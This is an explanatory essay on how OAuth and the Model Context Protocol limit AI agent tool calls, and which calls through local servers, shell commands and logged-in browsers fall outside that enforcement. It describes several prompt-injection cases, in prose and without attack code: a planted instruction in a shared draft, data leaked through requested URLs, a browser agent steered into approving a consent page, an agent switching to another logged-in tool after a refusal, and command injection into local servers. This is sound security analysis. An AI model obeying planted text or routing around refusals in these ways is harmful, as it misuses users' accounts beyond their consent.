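# AI agent tool calls that OAuth does not govern: local servers, shell commands and browser sessions

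## How OAuth and MCP decide what an agent may do

An AI agent is a language model joined to software that acts on the model's output. When a person asks for a task, the software carries it out, for example by sending an email, editing a file or querying a database. OAuth is a standard that lets an online service decide what a particular program may do with a user's account. When an agent reaches a service through OAuth, the service can check which program is calling, what the user allowed it to do, and whether that permission still holds. Agents also act through programs on the user's own machine, typed commands, and browsers where the user has already logged in. In those cases, the service may make no such decision about the agent.

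### From the model's output to an effect

Suppose a user keeps contract drafts in an online file store and asks an agent to summarize three of them and save the summary in the same folder. The model only produces text, so it cannot open the files itself. The software around the model first gives it a list of tools, each with a name, a description and a schema for its inputs. The model responds with a tool call, which is structured output that names one tool and fills in its inputs. The first call might name `read_file` and give the name of the first draft. The software passes the call to the program that carries out that tool and adds the result to the conversation. The model reads the result and produces another tool call or a final answer. The documentation of the Model Context Protocol (MCP), the common standard for connecting agent programs to outside tools, describes the same loop for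 a weather lookup.

The agent program is the software around the model. Examples include the coding agents Claude Code (from Anthropic) and Codex (from OpenAI), and the assistants that now come with some browsers. The model only proposes actions and the agent program carries them out, so a limit on those actions can sit in the agent program, in the operating system underneath it, or in the service whose data or functions the call reaches (here, the file store). OAuth applies in the service, which decides on its own machines whether to allow the request. Neither a bug in the agent program nor a misled model can switch off this service-side check.

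### How OAuth works

Before OAuth, a user who wanted one program to fetch data from another company's service had to give the program their password. *The OAuth 2.1 Authorization Framework* (Hardt, Parecki and Lodderstedt, 2026) lists the problems with this. The program has to store the password, typically in clear text. It can do everything the user can do for as long as the password works. The user cannot cut off one program without changing the password, which cuts off all the others too. The framework's example of using OAuth instead is a financial management service that reads a customer's transaction history at a bank without learning the customer's password.

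Four parties take part. The user owns the account. The client is the software that wants access, in the running example the agent program. The authorization server logs the user in and issues tokens. The resource server holds the data, so it is the service itself or the part of it that answers requests. One company often runs both servers, though OAuth does not require it. The usual sequence goes like this:

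1. The client opens the user's browser at the authorization server and passes along its own identifier and the permissions it wants.
2. The authorization server logs the user in and, normally, shows a consent page. The user types the password there, so the client never sees it.
3. If the user agrees, the authorization server sends the browser back to the client with an authorization code, a temporary credential.
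4. The client trades the code for an access token, a string that stands for the permission the user gave.
5. The client attaches the token to each request. The service validates the token and, if it is good, serves the request.

Step 4 has a safeguard called PKCE. The client generates a secret before step 1, at first sends only a value derived from it, and sends the secret itself when it redeems the code. Someone who intercepts the code can't redeem it without the secret.

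An OAuth grant is a user's recorded permission for one named piece of software to use an account within stated limits. The most familiar limit is the scope, a label on the token that specifies which kinds of operation the token permits. Each authorization server defines its own scopes, such as `email`, `channels:read` and `admin:org`, because OAuth doesn't define any. A client that only needs to read can ask for a read-only scope, and the authorization server may issue less than the client asked for. The scope has no effect unless the service enforces it when the token arrives.

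A scope defines what a token permits but not where the token works. The token's audience, the server it is meant for, sets that limit. Most OAuth tokens are bearer tokens, which work for anyone who holds them. *Resource Indicators for OAuth 2.0*, by Campbell, Bradley and Tschofenig, warns that if a bearer token is valid at two services, either one can take the token it receives and use it at the other. To prevent this, it adds a `resource` parameter, which the client uses to tell the authorization server where it intends to use the token. In its example, a user approves access to a calendar and a contacts list at two different addresses. The client first gets a token that works only at the calendar, with the scope `calendar` and a lifetime of 3,600 seconds, and later gets a separate token for the contacts.

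The third limit is that one-hour life, which reduces the damage from a leaked token. To spare the user a new login every hour, the authorization server can also issue a refresh token, which the client exchanges for new access tokens and never sends to the service. The user can revoke the program's access early, and the refresh token then stops working. A client can also cancel its own tokens, for instance when the user uninstalls it. *OAuth 2.0 Token Revocation* (Lodderstedt, 2013) specifies that such a request can also cancel the underlying grant and other tokens based on it. Neither kind of revocation affects other programs' access or changes the user's password.

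Hardt and colleagues explain that the authorization server evaluates the policy once, when it creates a token, and afterwards the service may only need to validate the token. Validation checks whether the token is genuine and unexpired, whether it was meant for this server, and whether its scope covers this kind of operation. OAuth has no way to check whether the user wanted this particular file opened at this particular moment.

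### The parts of MCP

OAuth long predates AI agents. Version 2.0 was published in 2012, and version 2.1, which combines it with later security advice, was still a draft in September 2026. MCP is much newer and uses OAuth for part of its work. It gives agent programs one message format for reaching tools, so developers do not have to write separate code for every pairing of agent program and service. MCP is widely used. In its July 2026 release announcement, the Model Context Protocol (2026) project reported close to half a billion monthly downloads of its main software kits, though that count includes automated installations.

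The Model Context Protocol's *Architecture* (2026) divides the work among a host, clients and servers. The host is the agent program. For each server it connects to, it creates one MCP client, which talks only to that server. An MCP server is a program that offers tools, and it can run locally or remotely. For example, Microsoft's code editor, Visual Studio Code, can act as a host with one client for a server run by the error-tracking company Sentry and another for a server that reads files on the user's own disk. By design, a server receives only the information it needs and cannot read the whole conversation or look into other servers. The host is responsible for keeping servers apart and handling the user's consent.

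"Client" therefore has a different meaning in each standard. When an MCP connection uses OAuth, the MCP client acts as the OAuth client, and the MCP server acts as the OAuth resource server.

Messages travel between client and server over a transport, and the Model Context Protocol's *Overview* (2026) of transports defines two standard ones.

- **stdio** (standard input and output). The agent program starts the server as a process on the same machine, and the two exchange lines of text over the channels a command-line program uses for its input and output. A server reached this way is a local server.
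- **Streamable HTTP**. The client sends each message as an ordinary web request to a single address, and the reply comes back the same way. A server reached over HTTP is a remote server.

Developers can also build their own transports. Messages mean the same thing on every transport, so a call to `read_file` has the same content whether it goes to a process on the laptop or to a data center. The transports differ in what surrounds the message. OAuth uses the headers of a web request and the status code of its reply.

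### One authorized call to a remote server

If the file store in the contract drafts example runs a remote MCP server that requires authorization, the MCP client sends the model's first tool call without a token, because it does not have one yet.

The server replies with status code 401, "Unauthorized". In the examples in the Model Context Protocol's *Authorization* (2026), a header on that reply gives the scope the call needs, `files:read`, and the address of a small document about the server. The client fetches the document, which names at least one authorization server. The Model Context Protocol's *Authorization Server Discovery* (2026) details how the client must try a set of standard locations if the header gives no address. This discovery step lets an agent program connect to a server its developers had never heard of. Attackers can also target it, so the client must check that the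 authorization server's description of itself matches the address it came from, and discard the description if it does not.

Next the client needs an identifier, because a grant has to name the software that receives it. Some clients have already registered with the authorization server. For the rest, the preferred identifier is a web address where the authorization server finds a description of the client.

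The client then opens the user's browser with a request that carries the scope `files:read`, the PKCE value, and the `resource` parameter, which holds the address of the file store's MCP server. The user logs in and approves, and the browser returns to the client with an authorization code. If the reply names an issuer, the client checks that it matches the one it recorded earlier before using the code. Without this check, an attacker who controls one authorization server could trick the client into sending that server a code from a legitimate one. The client exchanges the code for a token and resends the original tool call with the token in a header. The MCP server validates the token and returns the draft. Every later request must also carry the token.

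Binding the token to this one server depends on both the client and the MCP server. The client must always send the `resource` parameter, but the Model Context Protocol's *Authorization Security Considerations* (2026) acknowledges that this binds the token only if the authorization server supports the parameter. The MCP server must reject tokens that were not issued for it, and it must not forward the token it received. If it relays requests to another system, it needs a separate token from that system's authorization server.

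The agent reads the other two drafts with the same token. The model then produces a call to save the summary, but the token does not cover writing. The server replies with 403 "Forbidden", the error `insufficient_scope` and the required scope, `files:write`. The client then asks the authorization server for this scope in addition to what it already had, a procedure called step-up authorization. The user normally sees a second consent page. If the user agrees, the client gets a wider token and repeats the call. If the user declines, the client should give up after a few tries, and the folder stays unchanged.

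Real connections can be looser than this best case. If a server leaves the scope out of its first reply, the client may ask for every scope the server advertises. Step-up authorization also adds scopes without removing any. The client keeps its earlier scopes so that it does not lose access halfway through a job, a point that the Agentic AI Foundation's *Authorization in MCP 2026-07-28* connects to agents' long-running tasks. As a result, a token that starts as read-only may later allow more than reading. The procedure also needs someone present to give consent. In their November roadmap, the maintainers of the Model Context Protocol (2026) wrote that its authorization "assumes a person with a browser at consent time", while the caller is increasingly an agent working for a user who is not present.

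### Why an honest user still needs limits

Prompt injection occurs when an agent reads text, such as a web page, an email or a shared file, and the model follows something in it as if it were an instruction from the user. An attacker only has to put text where the agent will read it, and needs no access to the user's computer or account.

In the example, one of the three drafts might have come from the other side in the negotiation, with an instruction in small print for any AI system that opens it to overwrite the other two. If the model follows the instruction, the agent program sends a well-formed write request, and the outcome depends on the token. The user has approved only `files:read`, so the server refuses the request, and the user may see a consent page for write access that the task so far doesn't call for. Had the user already approved `files:write`, the server would accept the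 request, because a call caused by the planted text looks the same as one the user wanted. OAuth therefore limits what a successful prompt injection can do through that token to the access the user has granted, but it doesn't detect the injection.

All of this happens only if the developers of both the agent program and the server have built it. The Model Context Protocol makes authorization optional. It defines the procedure only for transports based on HTTP, and even there only recommends it. A local server on stdio is meant to take its credentials from its environment instead. Hardt and colleagues likewise designed OAuth for HTTP and put its use over any other protocol out of scope.

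## What counts as outside OAuth enforcement, and what is lost there

A tool call is inside OAuth enforcement when the service it reaches checks it against a grant that the user gave to the agent program making the call. Every other call is outside. A call can be outside for three different reasons.

A tool call may involve no remote service. When an agent deletes a file, edits source code or runs a test suite on the user's laptop, the operating system controls whether the action is allowed. The agent's processes normally run under the user's own account, so they have the same permissions as the user. OAuth does not apply because there is no service to issue or refuse a token.

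An agent may reach a service with an inherited credential, which is a password, key, token or cookie that the service issued to the user or another program and that the agent uses because it has access to it. Examples are a database password in a settings file and the session cookie in a browser where the user is still logged in to a bank.

Some services require no credential. Anyone can download a public web page or query an open weather service, and because MCP makes authorization optional, a remote MCP server may also accept calls from anyone. Although these calls reach nothing private, they can leak private data. An agent that has read a confidential file can put a line of it into the next web address it requests, and whoever runs that site can read the line in the server's logs.

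The classes apply to individual requests, and one tool call can produce several requests. For example, a single shell command can download a script from a public site, delete a folder and upload code with the user's saved key, so that call falls into all three classes.

### Why "bypass" is the wrong word

When an agent uses an inherited credential, the service usually still checks it. The service rejects an expired token and refuses any action that the user has no right to take. According to GitHub's *Authorizing OAuth apps*, a GitHub token can do only what its owner can do, and its scopes can limit it further.

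The service cannot tell the agent from the user, or from the program that the credential belongs to. If the user can delete a repository and the credential carries that right, the agent can delete it too. The service has no separate permission for the agent to look up, narrow or revoke.

The word "bypass" fits even less well when an agent deletes a file or opens a public web page, because neither action involves an OAuth check to get around.

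### Closing one issue by four routes

Developers keep code in repositories on GitHub, and each repository has a list of issues, such as bug reports and requests. Suppose a developer asks an agent to close issue 42 in a private repository. The agent could do this in at least four ways.

**The remote server with OAuth.** GitHub (2025) opened its remote MCP server as a public preview, with OAuth as the recommended login. The developer approves the agent program on GitHub's consent page, and the call that closes the issue carries the resulting token. If the token lacks a scope, the server requests it through step-up authorization (GitHub, 2026).

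For a private repository, the scope is `repo`. GitHub's *Scopes for OAuth apps* lists no scope that covers issues alone. The `repo` scope allows an app to read and write code and manage collaborators and webhooks, which are addresses that GitHub notifies when something happens in a repository. It applies to every repository the developer can reach, but if an organization restricts OAuth apps, an app that its owners have not approved can access only the organization's public material.

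A local server can use a personal access token, a string that a user generates in GitHub's settings and that a program presents in place of a password. The developer stores the token where the agent program can find it, and the program passes it to the local server at startup. GitHub's setup instructions for its local server leave users to choose which permissions they feel comfortable giving their AI tools.

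That choice matters a lot because GitHub offers two kinds of token. According to GitHub's *Managing your personal access tokens*, a classic token has broad scopes and reaches all the user's own repositories plus those of the organizations the user has access to. A fine-grained token works only for resources of a single owner, and the user can restrict it to chosen repositories and particular permissions. The developer could make one that reads and writes issues in this one repository and otherwise only reads public material. The local server looks up a classic token's scopes and hides the tools that the token could not use. With a fine-grained token, it shows every tool and relies on GitHub to refuse calls that the token does not permit.

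**The `gh` command.** The agent program opens a shell and runs `gh issue close 42`. `gh` is GitHub's own command-line program, and in this example the developer logged in to it weeks ago for ordinary work. According to GitHub's *gh auth login*, the default login goes through the browser, and `gh` then keeps the token in the system's credential store, or in a plain text file if it cannot use one. GitHub checks the request against an OAuth grant, but the developer gave that grant to `gh`, not to the agent. The agent's command produces the same request, with the same token, as one the developer types.

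The developer cannot narrow this token much for the agent. It needs at least the scopes `repo`, `read:org` and `gist`, and GitHub's *gh auth refresh* does not allow removing any of them. The `gist` scope allows writing gists, short files that a user can share with others. An agent that only has to close an issue therefore also has the permissions to copy private code into a shared file.

**A logged-in browser.** A browser assistant opens the GitHub issue's page and clicks the button that closes it. The browser attaches the cookie from the developer's login, so GitHub receives the same request as if the developer had clicked. No scopes apply to a web session, so the agent can use any page the developer can. This includes the settings page where users generate new access tokens, unless GitHub asks for a fresh login first.

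| Route | Who GitHub takes to be acting | Limits that GitHub applies | How to end the agent's access |
|---|---|---|---|
| Remote server with OAuth | The user, through the agent program's registered app | The user's rights within the app's scopes (here `repo`), plus any restriction by the organization | Revoke the app's authorization. Other programs keep working. |
| Local server with a personal access token | The user, through a token that names no program | The user's rights within the token's scopes, or within the chosen repositories and permissions if the token is fine-grained | Delete the token. Anything else that uses it stops too. |
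| `gh` command | The user, through GitHub's command-line program | The user's rights within the scopes of `gh`, which always include `repo`, `read:org` and `gist` | Revoke the authorization of `gh`. The user loses `gh` as well until the next login. |
| Logged-in browser | The user, in a web session | Everything the user may do on the website | Revoke the session. The user has to log in again in that browser. |

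OAuth enforcement covers only the remote server that uses OAuth. Local servers, shell commands and browser sessions all use an inherited credential, whose access can range from one repository's issues to the whole account.

### Hard cases

Many real set-ups mix features of these routes. Most can be classified by asking to whom the user gave the permission that the service is checking. Where the server runs and how the messages travel are poor guides.

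Calls that start over stdio can still be inside OAuth enforcement if the local server runs its own OAuth login. Under the Model Context Protocol, servers on stdio should get credentials from their environment, but that rule covers the link between the agent program and the server. The server can still log in to the service behind it in any way its developers choose. Anthropic documents an example in a version of its Claude Desktop app for organizations that get the Claude model through another provider. The app includes a copy of GitHub's MCP server and runs it as a local process. An administrator first registers an OAuth app for Claude Desktop with GitHub. When a user first opens the connector, Claude Desktop shows a short code and opens a GitHub page in the browser, where the user enters the code, reviews the requested access and approves it. This is the OAuth device flow, which does not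 need the browser to send anything back to the program. The resulting grant names Claude Desktop, and GitHub checks each call against it.

GitHub has since built a login into the local server. In July, GitHub (2026) described how the stdio server directs the user to a web address to log in. A change that GitHub (2026) developers prepared in June makes this the default on github.com, with the personal access token as an option. The classification is a bit less clear here, because the grant may name the MCP server and not the agent program. GitHub then could not tell apart two agent programs that start the same server. It still seems reasonable to count these calls as inside OAuth enforcement because, unlike `gh`, the server runs as part of the agent program and has access that the user approved for that purpose and can withdraw without losing any other tool.

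Developers sometimes run MCP servers on the user's side because it is simpler. In *Experiences with Model Context Protocol Servers for Science and High Performance Computing*, Pan, Chard and colleagues (2025) connected agents to Globus, a set of services that researchers use to move data and run jobs on supercomputers. Hosting the servers centrally would have meant passing users' tokens around securely, refreshing them and keeping sessions in step. They ran the servers locally instead, with a handler that starts the OAuth login and requests more scopes when a task needs them. These servers use both HTTP and OAuth, so a rule that local servers use stdio and therefore have no OAuth would misclassify them.

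A local bridge is a small process that the agent program starts on the same machine and that passes every message on to a remote server. It lets a program that only supports local servers reach remote ones. A call through the bridge is inside OAuth enforcement if the bridge runs the OAuth login and attaches the resulting token, because the remote server then makes the same check as it would without a bridge. If the bridge attaches a static key instead, the call is outside. The configuration file often shows which method is used. *The Secrets Agentic AI Leaves Behind* (Winterford, Vakil and colleagues, 2025), a survey of the credentials that agents use, looks at the remote server of Atlassian, which makes the project tracker Jira. A code editor on the user's machine can log in to that server through OAuth, so its configuration file needs only the server's address and no secret.

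Calls to a remote server can also fall outside OAuth. Anthropic's other connector for the same GitHub tools connects over HTTP to GitHub's hosted server, but it authenticates with a personal access token in the request headers, so GitHub sees no grant to Claude Desktop. An administrator can put one fixed token in every device's configuration, and Anthropic warns that every session then acts as the same identity.

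A call can also pass an OAuth check and still be outside OAuth enforcement for the service that holds the data. Suppose a company runs an MCP server in front of someone else's service. The server checks the user's grant properly, then calls the service with the company's own key. The service has a record of that key but not of the agent.

The fine-grained token that a developer makes only for the agent is harder to classify. The developer can name it after the agent, limit it to one repository, set it to expire in 30 days and give it to nothing else. GitHub then checks each call against those limits, and the developer can delete the token without disrupting anything else. This is almost a grant, but it doesn't identify the software using the token. The token's name is only a label that the developer typed in, GitHub has no record of which program holds it, and it would work just as well in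 a different program. Calls with this token are outside by the definition, but not much else is lost, so "outside" alone is a poor description of their risk.

*The Agent Clicks Approve* (Hossen, 2026) showed that an agent in a logged-in browser can itself press the approval button on a consent page. A grant can therefore exist without any decision by the user, and calls made under it can still count as inside OAuth enforcement.

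### What a check at the service provides

Why would it matter that a call is outside? The case for OAuth rests on four properties of the check that a service makes against a grant:

1. It identifies the software that is calling.
2. It can allow that software less than the user may do.
3. It runs where the agent cannot alter it.
4. The user can revoke the agent's access separately, and the service can log it separately.

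All four are open to serious objections, and some of the objections are right.

#### Identifying the software

A service that can tell which program is calling can set rules for that program. GitHub organizations can approve or block individual apps, and Atlassian let only listed AI applications connect to its remote server when Winterford and colleagues examined it. The service can also show people later which program acted. When a GitHub App (a newer kind of registration than an OAuth app) posts a comment for a user, GitHub shows the user's picture with the app's badge on it. An inherited cookie doesn't identify the program using it, so the service can't apply these rules or badges.

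OAuth identifies software on the user's own machine only weakly. The device flow in Claude Desktop uses no client secret, and the app's identifier is in a configuration sent to every device. A hostile program could copy the identifier, start a login and show the user a consent page with a trusted name on it. It could also steal a token that has already been issued.

This objection seems correct for malware but is much weaker for prompt injection, which compromises only the model. The agent program still sends its true identifier, so the service can apply whatever rule it has for that program.

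A program's name also does not show whether a developer or an agent made a decision, since both may work through the same code editor under the same registration. GitHub's *Enterprise AI Controls & agent control plane now generally available* (2026) introduced an audit log field, `actor_is_agent`, alongside fields for the user the agent acts for. *Audit log events for agents* adds an identifier that links an event to the agent session it came from. But enterprise owners find these events by filtering for Copilot, GitHub's own AI assistant, and an ordinary OAuth token from another company's editor does not carry that information.

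#### Allowing less than the user may do

This property is in principle the most useful of the four, as the read-only token in the contract drafts example shows, but scopes are often too coarse for it to help much. According to GitHub's documentation, OAuth apps cannot get read-only access to source code. To change the status of one issue in a private repository, an agent needs a scope that also lets it rewrite the code in all the user's private repositories. Winterford and colleagues found that the remote servers they assessed in 2025 gave agents the same access as the user who authorized them. With Atlassian's server, an administrator could not let agents edit wiki pages without also letting them modify Jira tickets.

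A local rule can be much finer than an OAuth scope. The agent program has access to the whole tool call, including the arguments, so it could allow "close issue 42 in this repository" and refuse everything else. None of GitHub's OAuth scopes can express that rule. Anthropic advises administrators not to rely on the `repo` scope alone to keep a session read-only. Its local GitHub connector has a `readOnly` setting that removes every tool that writes from the set given to the model, and a `toolPolicy` setting that controls whether calls to each tool need approval. Some irreversible actions, such as merging a proposed change into the code, need approval regardless of the policy.

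So the objection holds against many of the scopes that services offer today. It is weaker against checks at the service in general, because services can build finer ones, as GitHub already has. GitHub recommends GitHub Apps over OAuth apps because they offer fine-grained permissions, more control over which repositories the app can reach, and short-lived tokens. A GitHub App can still act for a user through OAuth. MCP also lets a server determine the required scope from the request's arguments, so a server could require one scope to close an issue and another to delete it, even if a single tool does both.

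A local rule covers only the calls that pass through the program that enforces it, whereas a token's limits apply in any program that uses the token. For example, Anthropic's `readOnly` setting restricts the connector but has no effect on a `gh` command that an agent runs in a shell on the same machine.

On this property, a server outside OAuth enforcement can be safer than one inside it. A local server with a fine-grained token for one repository does better than the remote server with OAuth and the `repo` scope.

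#### Running where the agent cannot alter it

An agent can't modify GitHub's servers, but its model can fail to follow an instruction, and if the agent has a shell, it may be able to edit the settings file meant to restrain it.

Hossen's experiments suggest how much the location of a check matters. A note on a web page steered a browser agent toward an action that the user's task had not authorized and that would give an outsider lasting access to the user's account or its data. Hossen calls the agent a confused deputy, a computer security term for a program that holds one party's authority but lets another party choose what to use it on. He tested the same policy in two places. The first was the prompt, where an instruction that only the user's task could authorize such actions still let 7 of 10 attacks through on Claude Haiku 4.5. The second was the service, which compared each request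 with a list of what the task allowed. The agents sent the forbidden request in all 70 attack runs, and the service refused it every time. It allowed the action in all 73 runs in which the user had asked for it.

Ten runs on one small model are weak evidence of how well a newer model would follow the instruction. The result for the service is more reliable because it does not depend on the model behaving well, though it does depend on the service having the right list. The test server was given that list in the experiment. A real service would have to know that an agent was controlling the session and get the list through a channel that web pages cannot write to. The check was also more specific than an ordinary OAuth scope because it compared the actual client and account, or the actual web address, with the task.

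An agent may be able to bypass a check that it can't alter. If the remote server refuses to close the issue and `gh` is logged in on the same laptop, the agent can use `gh` instead. Chen, Jing and colleagues (2026) measured this effect for local restrictions in *AuthorityLens*. They listed 599 outcomes, such as reading a file of credentials or deleting a file outside the project, and worked out which of them a coding agent could bring about under different settings. The Plan mode of one agent, OpenCode, removes the main agent's ordinary tool for editing files but leaves the shell. OpenCode could therefore bring about the same 537 outcomes in Plan mode as in its normal Build mode, all without the user's involvement. The Plan mode of Gemini CLI, Google's command-line agent, does remove the shell, and there the number was 76.

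None of those settings involved OAuth, but the same reasoning applies. A refusal by the service protects the issue only if the service would also refuse every other credential the agent can reach. The refusal therefore offers little protection on a developer's laptop full of old logins, and much more on a machine where the agent has only one narrow token.

Like the service, the operating system can enforce limits that a program inside them cannot lift. These are the only kind of limit available for preventing the deletion of local files, but they are a poor substitute for the service's own limits when the harm happens at the service. The operating system can allow or block a connection to GitHub, but the request inside that connection is encrypted, so the operating system normally cannot distinguish closing an issue from deleting a repository.

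#### Revoking and logging separately

If something goes wrong, the user wants to cut off the agent and keep working. If the agent program has its own OAuth grant, the user can do this with one change in the settings. If the agent uses the user's `gh` login, revoking it also cuts off the user's own commands, and revoking a shared key stops every script that uses it.

GitHub's *About token data in the audit log for an enterprise* describes records of actions outside the website that include the kind of credential, any scopes it has, and a hash that identifies the token without revealing it. An administrator who learns that a token has leaked can search for its hash and find everything that anyone did with it. The search returns the agent's actions if the agent has its own token, but mixes them with the developer's if the agent used the token of `gh`. Records of actions on the website contain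 no token data, so this search cannot distinguish an agent's clicks from the user's.

Any separate credential would offer the same benefit, so this is not an argument for OAuth in particular. A personal access token that only the agent uses has its own hash, and the user can delete it separately. Web sessions are also separate to some extent. GitHub's *Viewing and managing your sessions* describes a list in which the user can revoke sessions one at a time, so if an agent had its own browser profile and login, the user could end its session without being logged out elsewhere.

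I̶n̶ ̶s̶h̶o̶r̶t̶

The benefit comes from keeping credentials separate, and OAuth is one way to do that by default. Each program that goes through the login gets its own grant, whereas a user with a working key in a file has to make an effort not to reuse it for the next tool. Users who make that effort get most of the benefit without OAuth.

Revocation has limits on either route. Disconnecting the GitHub connector in Claude Desktop deletes the token stored on the device, but an earlier copy keeps working unless GitHub revokes the token. Revocation also stops only later calls, so an agent can merge a change or delete a repository before anyone revokes its access. The log then helps people repair the damage.

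## Local MCP servers and the keys they are given

The Model Context Protocol deliberately exempts local servers from its OAuth procedure. Under its authorization rules, implementations that use stdio "SHOULD NOT follow this specification, and instead retrieve credentials from the environment". In standards documents, "SHOULD NOT" is a strong recommendation that developers may set aside for a good reason. The clause does not specify how the server logs in to the service behind it, so a static key in an environment variable and an OAuth login both comply.

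According to Skverer's *State of MCP Server Security 2025* (2025), the first specification, from November 2024, did not cover where to store credentials. Almost all the sample servers released with it used broad credentials that never expired, such as classic GitHub personal access tokens. The March 2025 revision of the Model Context Protocol introduced OAuth and already contained the stdio clause. spinchange's *Literature* (2026), a machine-written summary of the November 2025 revision, lists the same rule. The fifth release, which went live on July 28, 2026 (Anthropic, *Bringing MCP 2026-07-28 to Claude*, 2026), tightened OAuth in several places. For example, some clients must now state their application type when they register (Model Context Protocol changelog, 2026). The stdio clause in the final text of that release is identical to the March 2025 version, and the draft of the next revision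 keeps it too.

### From the configuration entry to the service

Suppose a developer wants an agent to close an issue in a project tracker, and the only MCP server for that tracker is a local one. The entry in the agent program's configuration file might look like this:

```json
"tracker": {
  "command": "npx",
  "args": ["-y", "example-tracker-server"],
  "env": { "TRACKER_TOKEN": "the developer's key" }
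}
```

1. The developer creates a static key in the tracker's settings and pastes it into the entry.
2. The agent program reads the entry and has the operating system run the command. In MCP's official software kit for Python, as the security company Cantina shows, the command and its arguments are plain fields, and the kit starts the program they name. Here, `npx` downloads the server from npm, the public registry of JavaScript packages, unless the machine already has a copy. The `-y` skips the question of whether to install it.
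3. The new process runs under the developer's own account, so without a sandbox it can open any file the developer can. It also receives environment variables, which are named values that a program gets when it starts. `TRACKER_TOKEN` is one of them. Some agent programs also pass on variables from their own environment, which may include keys meant for other tools.
4. The agent program and the server exchange lines of text. This channel has no headers, as Model Context Protocol's *stdio* specifies, so it has no place for the token header or the 401 reply that OAuth uses.
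5. The model produces a call to close the issue. The server adds the key to a web request and sends it to the tracker, which checks the key and closes the issue.
6. At the end of the session, the agent program closes the server's input and the server exits. The key stays in the file and keeps working until it expires or someone deletes it in the tracker's settings.

In this sequence the model never needs to see the key, which is an advantage of the design.

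### How well the reasons for the exemption hold up

MCP was originally designed for a single application talking to a local process, according to the Agentic AI Foundation, the Linux Foundation body that now looks after it. The exemption makes sense in that setting. The Model Context Protocol tutorial on authorization describes OAuth as a way to establish that a user may access a remotely hosted server. A laptop with one user doesn't need that check, because the user's own agent program started the server and the server has no network port that a stranger could connect to. No outside party needs to redirect the user to a login page either.

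Model Context Protocol's *Security Policy* argues that a check between a local server and its client would protect neither. A malicious server can already run any code, because the user has started it, and a malicious client already controls the server process it started. The project therefore does not count it as a vulnerability if one can crash the other, and it warns that the stdio transport "is not a sandbox".

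These arguments convincingly explain why MCP does not require OAuth between an agent program and a server on the same laptop. But they give no reason to prefer a static key for the link between the server and the tracker, where the user's account is at risk. OAuth fits the tracker well because it runs on another company's machines, has many users and listens on the network. A local server can also open a browser for the login, as GitHub's does, and the tutorial lets local servers obtain credentials with or without a browser.

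Some of the premises are doubtful even on a laptop. Archestra's *MCP STDIO Command Injection*, a post by a company that sells software for running MCP servers, argues that calling stdio "local-only" assumes a single trusted developer and a single trusted server. A server on a single-user laptop can still receive text written by other people. If it builds a shell command from the inputs of a tool call, a prompt injection in a bug report can put the attacker's text into that command.

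The weakest premise is that the user can trust the server's code. An online guide by cloudstreet-dev compares running a local server to installing any other software, and advises people to choose well-known servers and review their source code. The comparison is fair, but installing other software is risky too. Glasp lists several attacks on npm in 2025, including the theft of tokens through the Nx build tools in August and a worm, Shai-Hulud, that hit more than 500 packages. A second version infected 796 packages in November, totalling 132 million monthly downloads. Many of these packages were established, so choosing a well-known one would not have been enough.

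Registries made for MCP may not filter much either. In *Anthropic design choice Exposes 150M+ Downloads and up to 200K Servers*, the security company OX Security reports that it tried to place a proof-of-concept malicious server in 11 of them and succeeded in 9. Red Hat advises developers and users to verify the integrity of all dependencies and scan them for malware. A company's security team can do that, but someone who copies an entry from a web page probably won't. The example entry doesn't name a version, so on a new machine `npx` installs whichever one the registry currently offers.

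OAuth would only partly help against a malicious local server. The server could misuse an OAuth token for as long as it was valid, and because it runs as the user, it could also search the disk for other programs' logins. A sandbox addresses that problem more directly. Local servers' exemption from OAuth matters more when the server is not malicious but its key leaks, or when the model makes a bad tool call and the key's permissions are too broad.

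### How common static keys are

Skverer, whose study is the usual source on how MCP servers handle credentials, found that about 88% of servers require them. About 53% rely on static API keys or personal access tokens, and 8.5% use OAuth. Another 26.4% mention credentials that the analysis could not classify. Of the servers that use API keys, 79% read them from environment variables.

Skverer works for Astrix, which sells a system for giving agents short-lived credentials. Astrix published the study with a free tool that fetches a server's secrets from a vault. The company therefore had a commercial interest in finding a problem, but the post describes the method in enough detail for readers to judge it.

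GitHub's search interface returns at most 1,000 results per query, so the team combined many narrow searches, for example by programming language or by the name of Claude Desktop's configuration file, and sorted the results by popularity. This produced 5,205 repositories. A language model then classified the servers by the credentials described in each repository's README file, the page that introduces a project to its users. The team did not analyze the servers' code.

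The sample probably contains fewer servers than the headline figure. Skverer reports that about 30% of the downloaded repositories did not contain a real server. He also puts the sample at about 19% of an estimated 20,000 servers, which would be about 3,800. He warns that the model was probably inaccurate in judging whether a server needs credentials, which makes the 88% figure less certain. The sample leaves out closed-source servers that companies host themselves, which plausibly use OAuth more often. A README can also describe an API key as one option among several.

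The main finding seems to hold whatever the unclassified servers use. Even if all of them used OAuth, its share would rise only to about 35%, well below the 53% for static keys. The 8.5% figure is less safe as a current estimate for MCP as a whole, though Darinor's *How to Vet an MCP Server Before You Install It* (2026) still used it that way in August 2026. The study also doesn't measure how much each key permits. It counts both a fine-grained token for one repository and a classic token for all of them as static.

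### Where the keys end up

An environment variable disappears when its process ends, so the agent program has to get the value again each time it starts the server, often from a plain-text configuration file. *Insecure credential storage plagues MCP*, by the security consultancy Trail of Bits, describes this pattern in official servers for Google Maps, Postgres and GitLab. On a Mac, the permissions on Claude Desktop's configuration file let any account on the machine read it.

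Chat logs can also contain keys. Some tools let the user type a key into the conversation and rely on the model to pass it to the server, which exposes the key to the model. Trail of Bits found that the code editors Cursor and Windsurf stored their conversation logs with similarly open permissions. A community-made server for the design tool Figma accepted the user's token through a tool call and then saved it to a file that other accounts on the computer could read and, on some systems, change. Someone who could change the file could replace the token with one for their own Figma account, and the user might then save private designs there without noticing.

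Stricter file permissions would keep out other accounts, but not malware that runs as the user. Trail of Bits recommends keeping credentials in the operating system's encrypted credential store, such as the macOS keychain. It suggests fixing permissions by hand only as a temporary measure.

A developer can also accidentally publish a key by uploading the configuration file with the rest of a project. Darinor cites a 2026 search by GitGuardian, which sells tools for finding leaked secrets, that found over 24,000 secrets in MCP-related configuration files on public GitHub. Of these, 2,117 still worked. A remote server with an OAuth login avoids this leak.

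### The dispute over how local servers start

In April 2026, OX Security objected to how MCP's official software kits start local servers. The kits run whatever command they receive without checking it. flyingpenguin's *Ox Security Report* explains that the command runs even if it does not start an MCP server. The agent program reports an error when the expected reply does not arrive, but the command has already run by then.

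This does little harm if the user wrote the configuration entry. But OX found products in which someone else could supply the command, including web applications that accepted server settings from visitors. In Windsurf, a prompt injection could run commands on the user's machine without a click. OX ran commands on six live commercial platforms, and its findings led to ten entries in the public register of software vulnerabilities.

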